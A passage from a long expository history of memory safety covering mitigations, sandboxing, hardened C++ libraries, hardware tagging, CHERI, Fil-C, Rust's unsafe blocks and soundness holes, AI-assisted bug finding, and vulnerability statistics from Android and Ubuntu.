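| Defence | Average slowdown | Worst slowdown | In use in 2013 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Non-executable memory | 0% | 0% | Yes |
| Address randomisation, libraries only | 0% | 0% | Yes |
| Stack canaries | 0% | 5% | Yes |
| Separate copy of return addresses | 5% | 12% | No |
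| Address randomisation, whole program (32-bit) | 10% | 26% | No |
| Control-flow integrity | 16% | 45% | No |
| SoftBound | 67% | 150% | No |
| SoftBound with CETS | 116% | 300% | No |

"SoK: Eternal War in Memory" concluded that defences that slowed programs by more than roughly 10% were rarely widely adopted, and some people in the industry put the limit at 5%. Most Linux distributions, for example, left the main program at a fixed address because varying the address slowed it by 10%. The slowdown figures are only rough because they come from each defence's own developers, who used different machines and test programs.

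Besides having low overhead, a defence had to work with existing libraries and unmodified source code, because most experts in industry considered even small manual changes impractical. Szekeres and colleagues blamed compatibility problems for control-flow integrity not being widely adopted. Its strictest form requires an analysis of the whole program, including every library it might load. Control-flow integrity did become popular later, and Watson and colleagues list it among current best practices.

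Hoare had been willing to accept a larger loss of speed in 1973. But C and C++ users in 2013, like the Fortran users who rejected his translator, already had programs that ran without checks, so they would have noticed the slowdown.

### Confining the damage

Software fault isolation, introduced in 1993, limits which memory a faulty component can damage. The component gets its own region of memory, and a tool adds instructions to its code that force every write into that region. If the region runs from 20000000 to 20FFFFFF in hexadecimal, the added instructions replace the first two digits of each address with 20, so a stray write to 35001234 goes to 20001234 instead. That write may corrupt the component's own data, but it cannot affect the rest of the program. Similar instructions keep jumps inside the component's code. These checks add some work at each write and jump, and isolation adds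 more whenever data passes between the component and the rest of the program.

Google's Native Client (2009) checked machine code from websites, much as the JVM verifies bytecode, and then ran it using fault isolation. WebAssembly, which the major browsers have supported since 2017, builds the limit on memory access into a portable instruction set. A C program compiled to WebAssembly keeps its data in a block of memory, its pointers are positions in that block, and the browser prevents any access outside it. Browsers also handle web pages in separate processes with few permissions, so an attacker who takes over one of these processes usually needs a second flaw to reach the rest of the computer.

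This gives the program with a stranger's picture decoder part of the protection that memory safety would. The decoder cannot alter the program's window from inside its block, even if it is written in C. But C's errors can still occur inside the block, where `a[10]` still reads whatever is next to the array. Somebody who sends a malicious picture can take control of the decoder and feed false results to the main program.

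Sharing data across a sandbox's boundary is also awkward. CHERIoT argues that this kept sandboxes from being used more widely, because programmers think in terms of objects that point to one another, whereas most sandboxes divide memory into fixed-size pages.

### Bounds checks at a third of a percent

In 2024 Google made bounds checks the default in C++ code across its production servers, with overhead far below the threshold. C++ programmers often keep data in standard library containers such as `vector`, an array that stores its own length. Normally, `v[10]` reads memory without comparing the index to that length. A hardened version of the library makes the comparison and stops the program if the index is too large.

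Google's *Retrofitting spatial safety to hundreds of millions of lines of C++* (2024) reports an average performance overhead of 0.30%. Unlike SoftBound, the library does not need to look up limits in a separate table, and the compiler can remove checks that repeat earlier ones. Google's engineers reduced the overhead from 0.35% by removing one unnecessary check. A critic suggested that the overhead might look small only because the surrounding code was inefficient. Carruth, a Google engineer, replied that the figure covered the whole production fleet, where a few extremely well-optimised services dominate. The figure still may not apply to a program that spends most of its time accessing array elements out of sequence.

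Google introduced the checks gradually, first in tests and then on a few services at a time. The checks exposed more than 1,000 bugs, some over ten years old, and fixing these reduced crashes from invalid memory accesses by 30%. The checks also disrupted an exercise in which Google's own staff tried to break into its systems. They are turned off in a few components, and some performance-critical code uses explicitly unchecked accesses, which reviewers examine.

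The library cannot check ordinary C pointers, and it does not prevent a program from using freed memory. Out-of-bounds accesses accounted for 40% of memory-safety exploits in Google's analysis of known attacks from 2014 to 2023, so even perfect bounds checking would not prevent most of them.

All three major C++ libraries already had hardened modes, each with different rules. Dargo (2026), in *C++26*, explains that the 2026 version of the C++ standard defines one hardened mode for all of them. Sutter, in *Poll*, writes that under the same standard, reading a local variable before it has a value will no longer be undefined behaviour.

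Old C code needs more work, because it has no containers that store their lengths. Apple's compiler lets a programmer state where the length is:

```c
void fill(int *__counted_by(n) buf, size_t n);
```

The compiler then checks each use of `buf` against `n`. The function still receives an ordinary pointer and a number, so existing code can call it, which was impossible with CCured's wider pointers. *Eliminating Entire Classes of Memory Safety Vulnerabilities in C and C++* (Coughlin, 2025) reports that Apple has applied this to millions of lines, at about an hour per 2,000 lines. At that rate, a billion lines would take half a million hours. For modern C++ that already used containers, the rate was more than 30,000 lines an hour. Coughlin considers the effort of adoption the biggest obstacle, which supports Szekeres and colleagues' point about changes to source code.

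### Checks in the processor

Apple moved some of the checks into hardware with the iPhone 17 in September 2025. Its system, Memory Integrity Enforcement, gives each small block of memory a secret tag and puts the same tag in pointers to the block. The processor compares the two at every access. Neighbouring blocks have different tags, so an overflow into the next block fails. When the program frees a block and reuses the memory, the tag changes, so an old pointer stops working.

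The protection depends on attackers not learning the tags, and Apple had to prevent them from inferring tags from the processor's timing. The tags also don't stop an overflow that stays inside one block, like the one from `name` into `is_admin`. Apple's *Memory Integrity Enforcement* does not give a figure for the slowdown, but says Apple devoted chip area, processor speed and memory to the protection. Apple's own researchers tried to adapt earlier real-world attacks to get past it and could not rebuild any of them. In May 2026 the security company Calif announced an attack on the macOS kernel that worked despite the protection. Its staff had built the attack in about a week with help from an AI model.

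CHERI, a research processor design, protects memory without relying on secrets. It replaces pointers with capabilities, which contain an address, limits and permissions. The processor refuses any access without a suitable capability, and no program can increase a capability's permissions. For example, the encryption code on a CHERIoT device calls the networking code to place incoming data in a buffer. It passes a capability that covers only part of the buffer, allows only writing, and cannot be kept after the call. The networking code can deliver its data but cannot read the buffer's earlier contents, even if an attacker has taken it over.

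CHERI stops a faulty program before any damage occurs, but it does not remove the fault. A Rust compiler rejects many of the same mistakes before the program ships. CHERIoT therefore recommends using safe languages on CHERI processors. CHERI protects only customers who buy the right hardware, as the Burroughs machines did.

### Fil-C

Fil-C is a compiler that makes existing C and C++ programs memory-safe on ordinary computers. Filip Pizlo began it in 2023 and was still its only active contributor in October 2025, when *Fil-C* (Alden, 2025) described how it works. Each pointer has a capability that the program cannot see or change. Fil-C stores an object's upper limit just before the object, and keeps the capabilities of any pointers the object contains in separate, hidden memory. To the program, a pointer still looks like an ordinary 64-bit address.

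In the four-line C example, `a[10]` exceeds the limit, so the program stops. In Fil-C, `free(a)` marks the object as freed, so reading `a[0]` afterwards also stops the program. A garbage collector reuses the memory only when no pointers to it remain, so an old pointer can never lead to a new object.

Fil-C's *InvisiCaps* puts the slowdown at about four times in bad cases, which is far above the 10% threshold. Structures that contain pointers also take up twice as much memory. Programs that spend most of their time waiting slow down less, and Alden used a Fil-C version of the Bash shell without noticing a difference. Pizlo has compiled a complete set of Linux programs with Fil-C, although the kernel and Fil-C's own runtime still need an ordinary compiler. Everything a program links to must also be recompiled, and Fil-C code cannot be combined with Rust.

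### Which one is memory-safe?

In July 2026 Andrew Kelley, the creator of the programming language Zig, proposed a Fil-C-inspired mode for the language, which he described as "actually memory safe (unlike Rust)". Pizlo had made the same criticism of Rust, because programmers can use `unsafe` blocks to bypass some of its checks.

The best argument for Fil-C is that the user doesn't have to trust the people who wrote the program, only Fil-C itself and the system underneath. With Rust, the user has to trust whoever wrote each `unsafe` block in every library the program includes, because one mistake there can corrupt memory that checked code relies on. CHERIoT cites a study that found 264 memory-safety bugs in published Rust packages. Many Rust programs also call C libraries, which Rust cannot check. Fil-C has no `unsafe` blocks, and it checks the C libraries too.

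Rust's defenders reply that a guarantee helps only the programs that can use it. *Memory Safety Absolutists* (Sarnacki, 2026) argues that programs that cannot use Fil-C, because of its garbage collector or the need to recompile everything, are often the ones that suit Rust. Rust's exceptions have done little harm in Android, where Google's estimate, quoted by Sarnacki, is 0.2 memory-safety vulnerabilities per million lines of Rust, against about 1,000 for C and C++. Fil-C turns memory-safety errors in C into crashes, which still affect users and which attackers can sometimes use to shut down a service. Programmers in the forum thread *New Proposal by Andrew* also objected that Fil-C does not catch overflows inside an object. Safe Rust would stop the overflow from `name` into `is_admin`, because it checks the array's own length.

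Whether Fil-C or Rust is safer depends partly on the definition of safety. In Azevedo de Amorim and colleagues' model, code cannot manufacture pointers. Fil-C enforces much the same rule, but a Rust program with `unsafe` blocks follows it only if those blocks are correct. Klabnik's definition requires defined behaviour by default and clearly marked exceptions. Rust meets this definition, but C compiled with Fil-C does not, because Fil-C does not remove undefined behaviour unrelated to memory.

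If an old C program can tolerate running several times slower, Fil-C offers stronger protection than Rust and does not require a rewrite. Rust is the better choice for a new kernel or browser engine, because its developers cannot accept Fil-C's overhead.

### Delay or extra time?

Partial protection may have allowed companies to put off replacing C. Watson and colleagues report that the rate of memory-safety vulnerabilities has stayed roughly constant for over two decades. They describe an arms race in which each mitigation hindered attackers only until the attackers found a way around it.

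This shows that mitigations left the errors in place, but not that companies would have replaced C if the mitigations had not existed. For most of those two decades, there was no obvious alternative language for writing kernels and browsers. Java needed a garbage collector, Ada had few users outside its specialist fields, and the first stable version of Rust did not appear until 2015. In 2013, Szekeres and colleagues still called rewriting everything in a safe language unrealistic.

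There is better evidence that the protections have since given companies time to move to safer languages. Google and Apple have invested heavily in protecting old code, and both are adopting memory-safe languages for new code. Google expects its bounds-checked C++ to be easier to connect to safe languages, and perhaps eventually to translate into them automatically. Users have benefited in the meantime. Apple says the only system-level attacks it sees on iPhones come from spyware makers, who spend millions of dollars to target a few people.

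Both companies are describing their own strategies, though, and they can afford to protect old code while replacing it. A smaller company might turn on the library's checks and keep writing C++.

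## Rust: compile-time safety and its unsafe blocks

Programmers who wanted to stop using C++ in kernels and browsers needed a memory-safe language without a garbage collector. Rust was the first such language to become widely used. Graydon Hoare started it in 2006 as a personal project while working at Mozilla, the maker of Firefox, and Mozilla later paid a team to develop it. Rust's main guarantee comes from a part of the compiler called the borrow checker. Matsakis (2018), in *An alias-based formulation of the borrow checker*, dates its first version to April 2012. The first stable version of Rust followed in May 2015.

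### Ownership and borrowing

The Rust compiler rejects this program:

```rust
let mut prices = vec![20, 35];
let first = &prices[0];
prices.push(50);
println!("{first}");
```

The first line creates a list that can grow, and the variable `prices` owns its memory. Every value in Rust has one owner, and the compiler inserts code to free the memory when the owner goes out of scope. The second line borrows from the list, so `first` refers to a number inside it without owning anything. The third line adds a number. If the list has no spare room, `push` allocates a larger block, copies the numbers there and frees the old block. The last line would then read freed memory through `first`, yet the equivalent C++ program compiles.

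At any time, a value in Rust may have either any number of shared references, which can only read it, or a single mutable reference, which can also change it. `push` needs a mutable reference to the list, and `first` is still in use because the last line prints it. If the programmer prints the number before calling `push`, the compiler accepts the program.

A garbage collector checks at run time whether a program can still reach a block of memory. The Rust compiler instead tracks the owner of each block at compile time and checks that no reference outlives that owner. The compiled program frees memory at fixed points, as a carefully written C program does, and so avoids the pauses and spare memory that Hertz and Berger measured in Java. When programmers cannot tell in advance which part of a program will use a value last, they can use a library type that counts the owners at run time.

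The same rule prevents data races, because two threads cannot access a value at the same time if either can change it. Library types such as locks let threads share changeable data by controlling access to it.

To apply the rule across a whole program, the compiler gives each reference a lifetime, the part of the program where it must stay valid. Programmers sometimes have to write lifetimes into a function's type so that the compiler can check each function without looking inside the others. The compiler also follows a borrow through data structures. In Matsakis's example, a program stores a reference to a number in a list, through a second reference, and then tries to change the number. The compiler rejects the change because the program uses the list afterwards.

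Adding one to that number would not have corrupted any memory, and the `push` in the first example would not have either if the list had had room. The borrow checker rejects both anyway, so programmers have to reorganise code that would have worked. Some ordinary data structures don't fit the rule at all. In a doubly linked list, for example, each item has a pointer from the item before and another from the item after, so neither neighbour can be its only owner.

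### What an unsafe block permits

A programmer can build such a list, or control a printer as C does, by marking part of the code `unsafe`. Inside an `unsafe` block a programmer may do four things that the compiler otherwise forbids:

- Read or write through a raw pointer, which is a plain address like a C pointer.
- Call a function that its author marked `unsafe`. Functions in other languages normally count as unsafe too.
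- Use a global variable that can change.
- Read a field of a union, which is much like a variant record in Pascal.

Programmers can also use `unsafe` outside blocks, writing `unsafe impl` to promise that a type has a property the compiler cannot check, such as being safe to share between threads.

Rust's other checks stay on inside an `unsafe` block. The borrow checker still checks ordinary references, types still have to match, and `v[10]` still gets a bounds check. To avoid that check, the programmer has to call a separate function, `get_unchecked`, which is also marked `unsafe`. Ada's `pragma Suppress` was broader, since it removed a kind of check from a whole region of code.

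The programmer also has to follow Rust's rules where the compiler no longer enforces them. If unsafe code creates two mutable references to the same value, the behaviour is undefined, because the compiler assumes when optimising that no other reference to the value exists. C has no such rule for ordinary pointers of the same type, so in this respect unsafe Rust is harder to write correctly than C.

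### Unsafe code behind a safe interface

Rust's designers did not expect application programmers to write much unsafe code. They expected library authors to write it, inside functions that nobody can misuse from safe code. The standard library has a function that splits an array into two parts so that a program can change both at once. A simplified version looks like this:

```rust
fn split(v: &mut [i32], mid: usize) -> (&mut [i32], &mut [i32]) {
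    let n = v.len();
    let p = v.as_mut_ptr();
    assert!(mid <= n);
    unsafe {
        (from_raw_parts_mut(p, mid),
         from_raw_parts_mut(p.add(mid), n - mid))
    }
}
```

A person can verify that the two parts don't overlap, because the first covers positions 0 to mid − 1 and the second covers mid to n − 1. The compiler can't verify this, so it would reject a version without `unsafe`. Callers don't need to write `unsafe` themselves, and whatever numbers they pass, the worst they can cause is a panic, Rust's term for stopping on an error.

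This depends on the `assert!` line, which stops the program if `mid` is too large. That line is ordinary safe code outside the `unsafe` block. If somebody deleted it, the program would still compile, but a caller could then access memory beyond the array. Searching a Rust program for `unsafe` finds every place where the compiler's checks are relaxed, but not all the code those places rely on. Library authors limit the problem by keeping the relevant data private to one module, so that a reviewer has to read only that module.

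For this scheme to work, one correct library has to stay correct when combined with any safe program and any other correct library. Ralf Jung, Jacques-Henri Jourdan, Robbert Krebbers and Derek Dreyer proved this for a model of Rust in *RustBelt* (2018). Progress and preservation do not apply to unsafe code, so RustBelt starts from what each type promises about behaviour. Write ⊢ e : τ if the typing rules give the code e the type τ, and ⊨ e : τ if e behaves as τ promises, however its author wrote it. The main results are

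⊢ e : τ implies ⊨ e : τ,

and that a complete program with the second property never performs an undefined operation.

The first result covers all safe code, but someone has to prove ⊨ e : τ by hand for each library that contains unsafe code. These proofs can then be combined with those about safe code, which assume only that the library behaves as its interface specifies. Jung and colleagues wrote computer-checked proofs for several important parts of the standard library, including locks and the types that count owners. They also found a bug in one of the lock types that let threads share data that was not safe to share.

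The model left out panics that run clean-up code, and traits, which let a library call operations supplied by its user. It also simplified how processors order memory accesses between threads. Several of the bugs researchers have since found in unsafe code involve these features.

### How programmers use the hatch

Two studies from 2020 counted unsafe code in Rust's public package collection. One of them, *Is Rust Used Safely by Software Developers?* by Ana Nora Evans, Bradford Campbell and Mary Lou Soffa, found the `unsafe` keyword in fewer than 30% of libraries. But the compiler could not fully check more than half of all the libraries, because they called unsafe code in other libraries. Java's `Unsafe` class had spread through libraries in the same way.

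In *How Do Programmers Use Unsafe Rust?*, Vytautas Astrauskas and colleagues tested what they called the Rust hypothesis, that programmers use unsafe code sparingly, keep it easy to review and hide it behind safe interfaces. They found that the hypothesis was only partly true. 76.4% of packages had no unsafe code of their own, and most of the unsafe code in the others was simple and well hidden, but some programmers used it extensively, especially to call code in other languages.

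These counts measure how much code needs review, not how often it is wrong. For *RUDRA*, Bae, Kim and colleagues (2021) built a program that searches unsafe code for a few known kinds of error, and ran it on all 43,000 packages in the collection in six and a half hours. It led them to 264 previously unknown memory-safety bugs, for which they obtained 76 entries in the public catalogue of vulnerabilities. The bugs they reported to Rust's own security database made up about half of all memory-safety bugs reported there since 2016. Some of the bugs were in code written by experts, including two in the standard library and one in the compiler.

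Most of these bugs count as bugs only because they are in interfaces declared safe. A C function is correct if it works when callers use it properly, but an unsafe block behind a safe Rust interface must stay memory-safe for every caller the compiler accepts, including one that supplies a faulty comparison routine or panics halfway through. A library can therefore contain a memory-safety bug that no existing program triggers, so 264 bugs in 43,000 packages do not mean 264 programs that an attacker could take over.

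When a Rust program calls code in another language, that code is harder to check. Rust programmers test unsafe code with Miri, an interpreter that stops at undefined behaviour, but Miri cannot follow a call into C. In *A Study of Undefined Behavior Across Foreign Function Boundaries in Rust Libraries* (2025), Ian McCormack, Joshua Sunshine and Jonathan Aldrich combined Miri with an interpreter that runs compiled C and reported 46 faults in 37 libraries. Three were in libraries with more than 10,000 downloads a day, and one was in a library that the Rust project maintains.

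Many of the 46 broke the rule about exclusive mutable references. It is normal for a C function to keep a copy of a pointer and write through it later, but the Rust compiler assumes that no other code can change the value. How many of these count as faults depends on rules that the Rust project has not finished writing. A newer proposal for the rules allowed considerably more of the code than an older one.

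### Holes in safe Rust

All of these bugs were in code marked `unsafe` or in C. Rust also has soundness holes, which let a program with no `unsafe` blocks break the safety guarantee.

The best known is issue 25860 in Rust's public bug tracker, which a contributor opened on 28 May 2015, 13 days after the first stable release. A reference to a reference makes sense only if the inner one stays valid at least as long as the outer one, so the compiler assumes this inside any function that receives one, even if the function's code doesn't state it. Another rule lets a program treat a function as if it had a slightly different type. As with the hole in Java's generics, the rules are harmless separately, but together they can make the compiler lose the assumption, and a program can then use a short-lived reference as if it were valid forever. Rust's developers have fixed the simplest form of the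 bug, but not all of it.

A second hole of the same age went unreported until 13 October 2026, when the programmer jsnell described it in *struct's lifetime requirements can be bypassed via covariant field assignment*. A Rust type can declare that it holds only data that stays valid for the whole run of the program. In some cases, the compiler did not enforce this when a program put a value into an existing object. The object's clean-up code, relying on the declaration, could then keep a reference to memory that the program had freed. Owen (2026) reports in *What the 11-year-old Rust borrow checker bug means* that contributors reproduced the problem in Rust 1.4, from 2015. The project gave it high priority but not the highest, on the grounds that a bug that went unnoticed for 11 years "cannot actually be that easy to hit". Exploiting it requires clean-up code written with malicious intent.

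That reasoning is sound for the people Rust was made for, who want protection from their own mistakes, but it is much less reassuring to anyone compiling code whose author may be hostile.

In November 2026 Microsoft's FORGE Lab reported holes of a different sort, in the unsafe code of the standard library, which nearly every Rust program uses. Bae (2026), in *Memory Safety Bugs in Rust Standard Library*, describes several, some of which a program written entirely in safe Rust can trigger. The lab found them with an AI system that scans software for vulnerabilities. Bae, who had also led the work on Rudra, sorts them into three patterns of misplaced trust:

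- Trusting code not to panic. Suppose a library function removes unwanted items from a list by calling a test that the user supplies. While it works, the list is in disorder, and the same item may appear twice. If the test panics at that moment, Rust's clean-up code may free the item twice.
- Trusting the user's code to be correct. A function might ask a user's type how many items it will supply, set aside that much room and write without checking. If the type gives too low a number, the function writes past the end.
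- Trusting the underlying system. Unsafe code may rely on something the operating system reports, such as the size of a piece of data, and go wrong if the report is false or out of date.

Rudra had searched for versions of the first two kinds of bug in 2021, so programmers had known about them for years, yet experts still made these mistakes in the most closely read library in the language. Bae thinks automated search can now find bugs of the third kind. Finding one requires understanding both the Rust code and the system it calls.

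### An AI model looks for counterexamples

Soundness holes last so long partly because a compiler behaves normally when it accepts a bad program. The hole stays hidden until somebody writes the unusual program that exposes it. A memory error in C is easier to notice because it may crash the program, and testing tools detect crashes.

Anthropic's *Finding logic bugs without general-purpose bug oracles* (2 December 2026) is about faults of this kind, in which software breaks a rule without crashing. The company's researchers tried four ways of using its Claude models to find them. The first two combine a model with an established testing tool, either for fuzzing, which feeds a program many varied inputs, or for symbolic execution, which works out mathematically which inputs lead a program down each path. In the third, the model reads the source code and looks for flaws. In the fourth, it tries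 to prove in ordinary prose that the code always obeys the rule, and treats any step it cannot justify as a possible bug.

They tested the methods on 21 bugs that developers had already fixed, giving the model the code from before the fix. The model then had to produce an input on which the old and the fixed versions behaved differently. Pogorelec (2026), in *Anthropic's AI bug tests uncover previously undisclosed flaws*, gives the results for Claude Mythos 5:

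| Method | Bugs found without being told the rule | Bugs found when told the rule |
|---|---|---|
| Reading the code | 11 | 20 |
| Attempting a proof | 8 | 21 |
| Fuzzing | 0 | 1 |
| Symbolic execution | 0 | 2 |

The proof method worked best when the model knew what to prove, which suits a safe language because its rule is known in advance. The researchers asked Claude to prove that safe Rust is type-safe, and it replied with several dozen counterexamples, some of which Rust's developers have already fixed (Faisal, 2026, *Claude Found a Seven-Year Bug in the Rust Compiler*). One is a five-line program that reads freed memory. The borrow checker fails to detect that evaluating an array index can free the value a program has just borrowed. Rust contributors traced the bug to April 2019, when the project switched on a new version of the borrow checker. The bug was still open on 3 December 2026,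 along with about 178 other soundness issues.

The company calls these bugs rather than security vulnerabilities because an attacker cannot use them against an ordinary Rust program from outside. Nicholas Carlini, who led the Rust work, is not a Rust expert and asked developers who are to confirm the example before he filed it. More candidates were waiting for the same check, which was meant to avoid flooding the project with poor reports. The model can evidently produce counterexamples faster than people can verify them and fix the bugs they expose.

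The same method uncovered more than 100 soundness bugs in Linux's eBPF verifier. eBPF lets users run small programs inside the kernel, for instance to monitor network traffic. The verifier checks each program before it runs and is meant to reject any that might access memory it shouldn't or run forever. It plays the same role for the kernel as the bytecode verifier does for Java. A program that passes runs with the kernel's access to the machine, so a soundness bug in the verifier is more serious than one in the Rust compiler, which was not designed to stop hostile programs.

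Such bugs are also getting easier to find. On the 21 known bugs, with no hint about the rule, Claude Sonnet 4.5 (2025) found one by reading the code, Claude Opus 4.5 found five and Claude Mythos 5.2 (November 2026) found 15. An attacker with a similar model could now search for holes that Rust's developers could once assume would stay obscure because nobody had hit them in ten years.

### Repairing the compiler and proving the library

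The Rust Project's *Project Zero* is a plan to fix every known soundness bug in the type system, until `unsafe` is the only way to cause undefined behaviour. The stated reason for urgency is that somebody will probably build an attack on one of these bugs if they stay open, although they have rarely if ever affected real systems.

They are still open because the obvious repairs would also make the compiler reject correct programs that people already use. Better repairs need a compiler that can reason about more cases, so the project's first step is to replace the trait solver, the component that works out which types support which operations. Compiler developers have been building the new solver for several years and planned to finish it in 2026. They can fix self-contained bugs in the meantime. Once the new solver is in place, the project plans to fix the bugs about unstated assumptions,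 such as issue 25860, and then write a formal description of what the solver should do, so that developers can find new holes before release. Several of these tasks are scheduled only for "Future".

Any fix that breaks existing code will start as a warning, just as Java's developers have been using warnings to close their escape hatches. Rust programmers whose code depends on a soundness hole have probably never heard of the hole, whereas Java programmers knew they were using `Unsafe`.

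Project Zero deals with the type system and would not have prevented the problems FORGE Lab found in the standard library. *Verifying the Rust Standard Library* counts about 7,500 unsafe functions in that library, plus 3,000 safe functions that contain unsafe code. Since November 2024, the Rust Foundation, a non-profit that supports the language, and Amazon's cloud division have offered prizes for proving parts of the library free of undefined behaviour. The Rust Foundation's *How the Rust Standard Library Verification Contest Scaled Past Manual Proof Engineering* (2026) describes the contest's progress.

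For the first year, people wrote the proofs by hand. Most used Kani, a tool that checks a function for every possible input within set limits. The programmer writes a harness, a short piece of code that calls the function with symbols instead of actual values, and Kani searches for values that would cause an error. Zech (2026), in *Kani*, explains how programmers can remove the limits by adding contracts, which state what a function requires and what it guarantees. Contributors wrote 725 harnesses, nearly all with contracts, but progress levelled off around October 2025. The library has about 34,000 functions and changes every six weeks.

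Amazon's engineers then built a tool that writes harnesses automatically. It produced 16,748, and Kani verified 11,970 of them, or 71%. Kani now repeats more than 16,000 checks whenever somebody changes the code. The automatic proofs cover errors such as out-of-bounds access, dangling pointers and reads of uninitialized memory, but not data races. The Rust Foundation cautions that not all of the verified harnesses are equally significant. Trying every input works best when the inputs are numbers or arrays. In the first two of Bae's patterns, the dangerous input is a piece of the user's code, and no simple range of values represents everything such code might do. RustBelt's proofs can handle such code, but experts have to write them one library at a time.

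### Forty-four bugs and no memory errors

Even a perfect compiler and a proved library would not prevent most of the mistakes a program can contain. In 2025, Ubuntu, a popular version of Linux, began replacing the small commands that copy, sort and delete files with versions rewritten in Rust. In April 2026 its maker, Canonical, disclosed 44 vulnerabilities in the Rust versions, most of them found by an outside audit it had paid for. *Bugs Rust Won't Catch*, by the Rust consultancy corrode, goes through the list and finds no memory errors.

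The largest group of bugs came from checking a file and then acting on it in a separate step, using its name both times. Between the steps, another user can make the name refer to a different file. A program with an administrator's powers can then overwrite the wrong file. The fix is to open the file once and keep the handle, because a handle refers to the file itself and works much like a capability. Rust's standard library made this mistake easy, since its most convenient functions all take a name. C programmers use handles more naturally. Because of these bugs, Ubuntu 26.04 kept the old C versions of the commands for copying, moving and deleting files.

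The other bugs were more varied:

- The command that changes permissions had a safeguard against altering the entire disk, but it compared names as text and missed other ways of writing the same location.
- The sorting command halted on a file name that was not valid Unicode text. The C version treats names as plain bytes.
- One command reported success if the last file succeeded, even when earlier ones had failed.
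- The command for stopping programs read one ambiguous option differently from the C version, and could stop every program the user had running.

As on Ariane 5, a defined stop can still do harm. If the sort is one step of a nightly backup, the backup fails.

For comparison, corrode lists nine memory errors that the developers of the C originals fixed between 2021 and 2026, in commands such as `pwd`, `sort` and `split`. The consultancy takes the contrast as evidence that Rust removed most of what usually goes wrong in C, with two reservations. The C commands are 40 years old, so their memory errors have had far more time to come to light, and an audit that finds no memory errors does not prove there are none. Some of the 44 bugs came from rewriting the commands. Other people's scripts relied on small decisions made in the old commands over decades, and the new authors could not have used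 a type checker to identify them.

Logic errors are common in safe Rust. *Does Safe == Secure?* (2025) examined 135 security advisories about safe Rust code from 2021 to 2025 and put logic flaws, such as failing to check input properly, first among its four categories.

### Promises that Rust never made

Some gaps in the guarantee lie outside the program. Linux exposes a program's own memory as a special file. The program can open that file and write to it with ordinary safe functions, changing any value in its memory and bypassing the compiler's checks. Rust's developers do not regard this as a soundness hole, because the operating system does the writing and their documentation limits the guarantee to what the program itself can do.

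This matters little to most programmers, but some researchers have relied more heavily on the language. Theseus and RedLeaf, two experimental operating systems from 2020, are written in Rust and do without the hardware barriers that normally keep programs out of one another's memory. All their components share one address space, and the compiler is supposed to stop them from interfering with one another. Components can then call one another as quickly as ordinary functions. Burroughs made a similar choice in the 1960s when it relied on approved compilers, though it also had hardware checks.

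Such a system needs every component without `unsafe` to be harmless, whoever wrote it, and Rust does not guarantee that. A malicious component could use any of Rust's open soundness holes to access other components' memory, and the project ranks those holes by how likely an honest programmer is to run into them. Rust also allows safe code to loop forever or use up the machine's memory.

Theseus also uses Rust's clean-up code to reclaim a component's resources when the component stops. Rust normally runs that code when an owner goes out of scope, but safe code can skip it by calling the standard function `forget`. Shortly before the first stable release, Rust's designers found that a function in a thread library relied on clean-up code for memory safety. They decided that failing to clean up does not count as unsafe, and they withdrew the function.

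## 2019 to 2026: measured results, government pressure and machine-written ports

Large companies adopted Rust despite these gaps because their alternative for a kernel or a browser was C or C++, which checked far less. Programmers had known that memory errors were dangerous since at least the Morris worm. Around 2019, several companies began to count those errors and publish the results.

### Where the 70% comes from

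In February 2019 Matt Miller, a security engineer at Microsoft, told a conference that memory-safety errors had made up about 70% of the vulnerabilities the company fixed each year since 2006. The figure covered flaws listed in CVE, the public catalogue of vulnerabilities. The share had hardly changed in twelve years, although Microsoft kept adding defences against exploitation.

Google's Chrome team found the same figure in 2020 using a narrower set of bugs. Of the 912 bugs since 2015 that the team had rated high or critical and that had reached the stable version of the browser, about 70% were memory errors. Around half of those memory errors were uses of freed memory.

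Both figures describe large programs written mostly in C and C++. An online shop written in Java has few memory errors of its own, so the figure does not carry over to software in general. The counts also include only flaws that somebody found, and testing tools find memory errors more easily than most other kinds. Records of real attacks avoid that problem, and they point the same way. Alex Rebert and Christoph Kern of Google, whom OSnews quotes, reported that two thirds of the zero-day exploits detected in use relied on memory corruption. (A zero-day exploit attacks a flaw before its maker has a fix.)

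### Android stops adding unsafe code

In 2019 memory errors made up 76% of the vulnerabilities in Android, Google's operating system for phones. Google left most of the old C and C++ in place and moved new development to memory-safe languages. Much of the new code was in Java or Kotlin, and from 2021 Android's developers could also use Rust where they had previously needed C or C++. By 2024 memory errors had fallen to 24% of vulnerabilities, as Google (2024) reported in *Eliminating Memory Safety Vulnerabilities at the Source*. Vander Stoep (2025), in *Rust in Android*, put the share below 20% for 2025.

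The number of memory-safety vulnerabilities fell along with their share. The security company Curtail gives 223 for 2019, and Google projected 36 for 2024. Together with the percentages, these numbers imply that other vulnerabilities rose from about 70 to about 114 a year. That rise also lowered the memory-safety share, which would have been about 34% in 2024 instead of 24% if other vulnerabilities had stayed at 70.

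### Why the old code could stay

Google's explanation is that vulnerabilities in old code become rarer by themselves, as people find and fix them. Suppose that people are equally likely to find any given vulnerability in any year, and that the average one lasts τ years. Code that starts with N vulnerabilities then has

N · e^(−t/τ)

left after t years. In Android and Chromium, the open-source project behind Chrome, Google found that five-year-old code had 7.4 times fewer vulnerabilities per line than new code. That corresponds to a τ of 2.5 years. Lifetimes from an academic study of other projects gave a ratio of 3.4, or a τ of about 4.1 years.

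Now take a company that finds 100 memory errors a year and adds 100 more in its new code, so that the total stays level. It then starts writing all new code in a safe language and leaves the old code alone. It would go on to find this many a year:

| Years after the change | If τ is 2.5 years | If τ is 4.1 years |
|---|---|---|
| 0 | 100 | 100 |
| 1 | 67 | 78 |
| 3 | 30 | 48 |
| 5 | 14 | 30 |
| 10 | 2 | 9 |

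The company gets most of the benefit within five years without rewriting any old code. Rewriting old code helps less because most of its errors are already gone, and a rewrite can introduce new ones, as Ubuntu's Rust commands did.

Android's count fell to 16% of its starting figure in five years, close to the faster column, even though its developers were still adding C++. If new errors had continued at half the earlier rate, the model would predict 57%. Google acknowledged that the results were better than its own simulation had predicted and suggested that its parallel work on making the unsafe code safer had helped.

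Google had already reported a fall to 85 vulnerabilities in 2022, but until then its developers were adding far more C++ than Rust to the platform, so Rust cannot explain much of the early improvement. The move to Java and Kotlin probably explains some of it, and better testing and a memory allocator designed to resist attacks may also have helped.

The decay rate also depends on how hard people look for bugs. Groß (2026), in *Fuzzers vs. AI*, compared two tools that Google runs on V8, Chrome's JavaScript engine. In six months, a tool based on a language model found 45 vulnerabilities and an established fuzzer found 37, with only about a quarter in common. AI tools have also found hundreds and sometimes thousands of bugs in other programs that fuzzers had already tested heavily. Old code evidently contains more errors than its record suggested. Developers can now remove these errors faster,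 but attackers with similar tools can find them too.

### One near miss in five million lines

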